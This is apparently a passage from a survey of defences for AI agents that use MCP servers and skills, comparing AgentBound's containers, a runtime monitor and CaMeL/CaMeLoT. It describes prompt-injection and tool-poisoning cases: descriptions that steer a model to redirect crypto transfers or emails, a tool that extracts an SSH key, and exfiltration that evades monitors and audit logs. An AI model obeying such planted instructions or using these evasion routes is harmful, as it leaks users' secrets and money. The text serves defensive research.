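Suppose an agent may read files and send email, and it calls a tool that adds numbers and declares that it needs no permissions. The call gets only the permissions that the agent has and the tool declares. Here there are none, so the call can't open a file or send anything. But this limit alone wouldn't stop Invariant Labs' first attack, because the agent used its own file access to read the SSH key before it called the adding tool.

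Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2025), in *AgentBound*, enforce declared permissions for local MCP servers. Each server comes with a manifest that lists what it needs, in terms borrowed largely from Android. In simplified form, the manifest of a server that fetches documentation might look like this:

```json
{
  "description": "Fetches documentation from the web.",
  "capabilities": ["mcp.ac.network.client"]
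}
```

The first time the server runs, the user names the web addresses it may contact. AgentBound then starts the server in a container, an isolated environment with access only to those addresses and any folders the user has chosen. If the adding tool in Invariant Labs' attack ran locally under these rules, it would still receive the key but would have no network connection to send it over. If the tool ran on a remote server, the key would already have left the machine.

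The broad categories in a manifest give little protection unless the user also limits the server to specific folders and addresses. Bühler and colleagues had models write manifests for 296 popular servers, and 83.1% of the servers needed the network while 74.1% needed to read files. At least 57% therefore needed both, as would a program that steals files. If manifests listed only these categories, an honest server and one that steals files could have the same manifest.

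A company could generate manifests for existing servers this way instead of relying on their developers to write them. The researchers compared generated manifests with handwritten ones for 48 servers. The two versions matched exactly for 28 servers, and 23 of the 29 individual errors were missing permissions. A missing permission might stop the server from working, but it wouldn't expose the user's data. However, the generator requires the server's source code.

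### What AgentBound blocked

Bühler and colleagues tested AgentBound on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers, four from one public collection and ten from another. They report that it blocked eight of the attacks outright, though elsewhere they describe one of the eight as out of scope. Two of the blocked attacks came from a maps server and a weather server that secretly contacted a different address. Others tried to read private files or run commands. Five attacks got through, and the last server combined several attacks with mixed results.

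AgentBound failed to stop one attack that used a time server with a poisoned description. The description contained instructions for the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers to another address whenever it used a separate wallet tool. AgentBound detected no violation because the wallet tool contacted the same service as usual and only the recipient was different.

These results may overstate how well AgentBound works, because the researchers wrote the manifests for the ten challenge servers themselves. A malicious author would ask for more access and invent a reason for it. AgentBound also downloads and installs a server's package inside the container before it restricts the network. An installation script like the one in mcp-server-postgres could still send data out, although it would find far less there than on the user's own machine.

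The protection causes little delay. Containers usually added a few tenths of a second when a server started and less than a millisecond to each operation afterwards.

Skills don't get this isolation automatically, so their safety depends partly on where they run. Li and colleagues note that the same SKILL.md file runs in a sandbox through Anthropic's API but with the user's full privileges in Claude Code, unless the user turns on its isolation modes.

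### A monitor that loses track of paraphrases

A container controls each server separately, but data can leak when an agent reads something with one permitted tool and sends it with another. The runtime monitor that Badhe and Tiwari tested in SkillSec-Eval watches for such transfers. It cut the share of attacks that reached their final privileged action, such as sending a secret to an outside address, from 100% to 23%. It also blocked 87% of unauthorized operations. (The 23% and the 87% add up to more than 100% because one counts attacks and the other counts individual operations.)

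That is a large improvement, but the paper doesn't report the number of attacks or how often the monitor blocked harmless work. It also lists least privilege as a separate research question but reports no result for it.

The monitor's main weakness is that it loses track of a secret once the model has paraphrased it. This is hard to fix while the same model reads the data and decides what to do next, because software outside the model can't detect which parts of the model's input influenced a sentence.

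### How CaMeL works

CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, avoids this problem by dividing the work between two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe the design and extend it. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Dana some travel dates, and says that her address is in her last message. CaMeL proceeds in four steps:

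1. A planning model reads the request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. It does this before the agent has opened Dana's message.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and calls the tools. It fetches the message and labels it as outside data.
3. A second model reads the message and returns the address. This model has no tools, and the interpreter stores its answer in a variable without showing it to the planning model.
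4. Before sending the email, the interpreter runs a policy, a small function that looks at the tool, its arguments and their labels and then allows or denies the call.

The program might look like this:

```python
message = get_last_message("Dana")
address = ask_reader("Find Dana's email address.", message)
send_email(address, "I arrive on May 3 and leave on May 6.")
```

If an attacker has planted an instruction in Dana's message to delete the user's files, nothing happens, because the program contains no such step. Separating the models doesn't stop the attacker from tricking the second model into returning a false address, so CaMeL adds the labels, which record where each value came from and who may read it. A policy could block emails to an address that came from an outside message, or block sending a private document to anyone who isn't on its list of readers.

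The labels remain attached when data is paraphrased. If the second model summarizes a confidential report, the interpreter tracks the report as the input and gives the summary the same label. *CaMeLoT* has four levels of trust and assigns each new value the level of its least trusted input. Zhao and colleagues use the same rule in their scanner, but CaMeL applies it while the agent is working.

The policies still require judgment. A rule against using addresses from outside messages would stop the attack on Dana's address, but it would also block the user's reasonable request. The agent would have to ask the user to confirm the address, which again relies on the user paying attention, though the question is a much better one.

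### Poisoned descriptions on the trusted side

Once the planning model has written a plan, CaMeL protects it from data that arrives later. Tool descriptions arrive earlier, because the planner needs them to write a program that calls the tools. *When the Manual Lies* (2026), a benchmark of poisoned MCP tools, likewise treats an agent's plan as depending on the descriptions of all available tools.

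According to Nikolaou and colleagues, CaMeL trusts the user's prompt and the system prompt. *TRUSTDESC* (2026) explains that applications load developer-written tool descriptions into the system prompt. If an application using CaMeL does the same, a poisoned description becomes trusted input. This is an inference from the two designs, not a measurement, but it's hard to see how the planner could avoid the problem without some other check on the descriptions.

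In Invariant Labs' second attack, a poisoned description claimed that all emails had to go to one particular address. A planning model that followed this description might write the address directly into the program. *CaMeLoT* gives values written into the program its highest level of trust, so a policy against untrusted recipients would let the email through. A policy based on permitted readers could still protect a confidential attachment, because the attacker wouldn't be on the attachment's list.

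Skills create a harder choice. If the planning model reads SKILL.md, the skill's author can influence the plan. If only the second model reads it, the skill can't supply the steps the user installed it for.

The planner therefore depends on someone checking the descriptions first. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) found that the client applications it examined trusted whatever metadata a server sent without checking it. *TRUSTDESC* proposes replacing developers' descriptions with generated ones that an application can trust. Software could derive such descriptions from a tool's code, but not for a remote server whose code outsiders can't read. For a short list of tools, a person can write the descriptions by hand.

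### What CaMeL costs and what has followed it

An agent that uses CaMeL completes fewer tasks, because some tasks don't fit into a plan written in advance. If a user says "do whatever the email asks", the planning model can't write the steps without reading the email. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which adapts the design to groups of agents, calls the loss "comparatively modest" on AgentDojo, a common benchmark for prompt injection, and predicts that it will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. That is a qualitative judgment, and a company would have to measure the loss on its own tasks. *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower than defenses that only filter text or add warnings to a prompt.

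*CaMeLoT* deals with a different drawback. CaMeL checks each call just before making it, so an agent may complete nine steps of a task and then discover that a policy forbids the tenth. *CaMeLoT* examines the whole program before it runs. It translates the program into a finite set of states and checks every possible path through them against rules such as

AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

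AG means "in every state on every path". The rule forbids the program from sending money if the recipient or the amount comes from untrusted data. If a path breaks the rule, the checker reports that path, and the planning model can rewrite the program.

Rules can also cover the order of events. For example, a security team could require approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. If a plan leaves out that step, *CaMeLoT* can find the omission before the agent acts.

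By design, the check assumes that a loop could run any number of times, so it sometimes rejects a safe program. It also keeps CaMeL's assumptions about what to trust, so it adds no protection against poisoned descriptions.

Another project, *CapLite* (2026), is designed for agents built on small language models, which may struggle to write correct programs and policies. According to its full title, it does not use security rules written by a model.

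### Access that the task needs

The table compares how the two main designs would handle four attacks described earlier. Its entries are judgments based on how the designs work, because nobody has run these particular tests.

| Attack | Container around a local server | CaMeL's rules |
|---|---|---|
| adding tool that asks for an SSH key | can stop the server from sending the key on | can refuse to give the tool a private file |
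| description that redirects emails | no effect, because the email tool may send email | may treat the attacker's address as trusted |
| postmark-mcp | no effect, because the copy leaves through Postmark's own service | no effect, because the tool adds the copy internally |
| money-radar | no effect, because the skill only needs to read a web page | can fix the steps but not the advice |

A sandbox can't stop an attacker from misusing access that the task needs. An agent that sends email needs permission to do so, and that permission covers harmful messages as well as useful ones. Bühler and colleagues acknowledge this limit.

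Audit logs can also miss data theft. In February 2026, the company Mitiga published a test skill that copied a developer's entire codebase to an outside server in four interactions with the user, while the audit log stayed empty. Because reading code and using the network are normal for a coding agent, Li and colleagues argue that a monitor would need information about what this particular skill was supposed to read and where it was supposed to send it.

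Tighter rules can reduce the damage without eliminating it. If an agent pays invoices, ordinary software can restrict it to suppliers already in the company's records and limit how much it spends in a day. An attacker who controls the agent completely could then make it overpay a real supplier, but couldn't add a new one. If emails were held for a few minutes before sending, a user who checked them could cancel one.

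Spending limits and recipient lists suit actions with an amount or a recipient that software can check. They don't apply to money-radar, whose harm was in the advice it gave. A user could still catch the harmful advice by reading the skill's instructions or by asking a second agent without the skill the same question.
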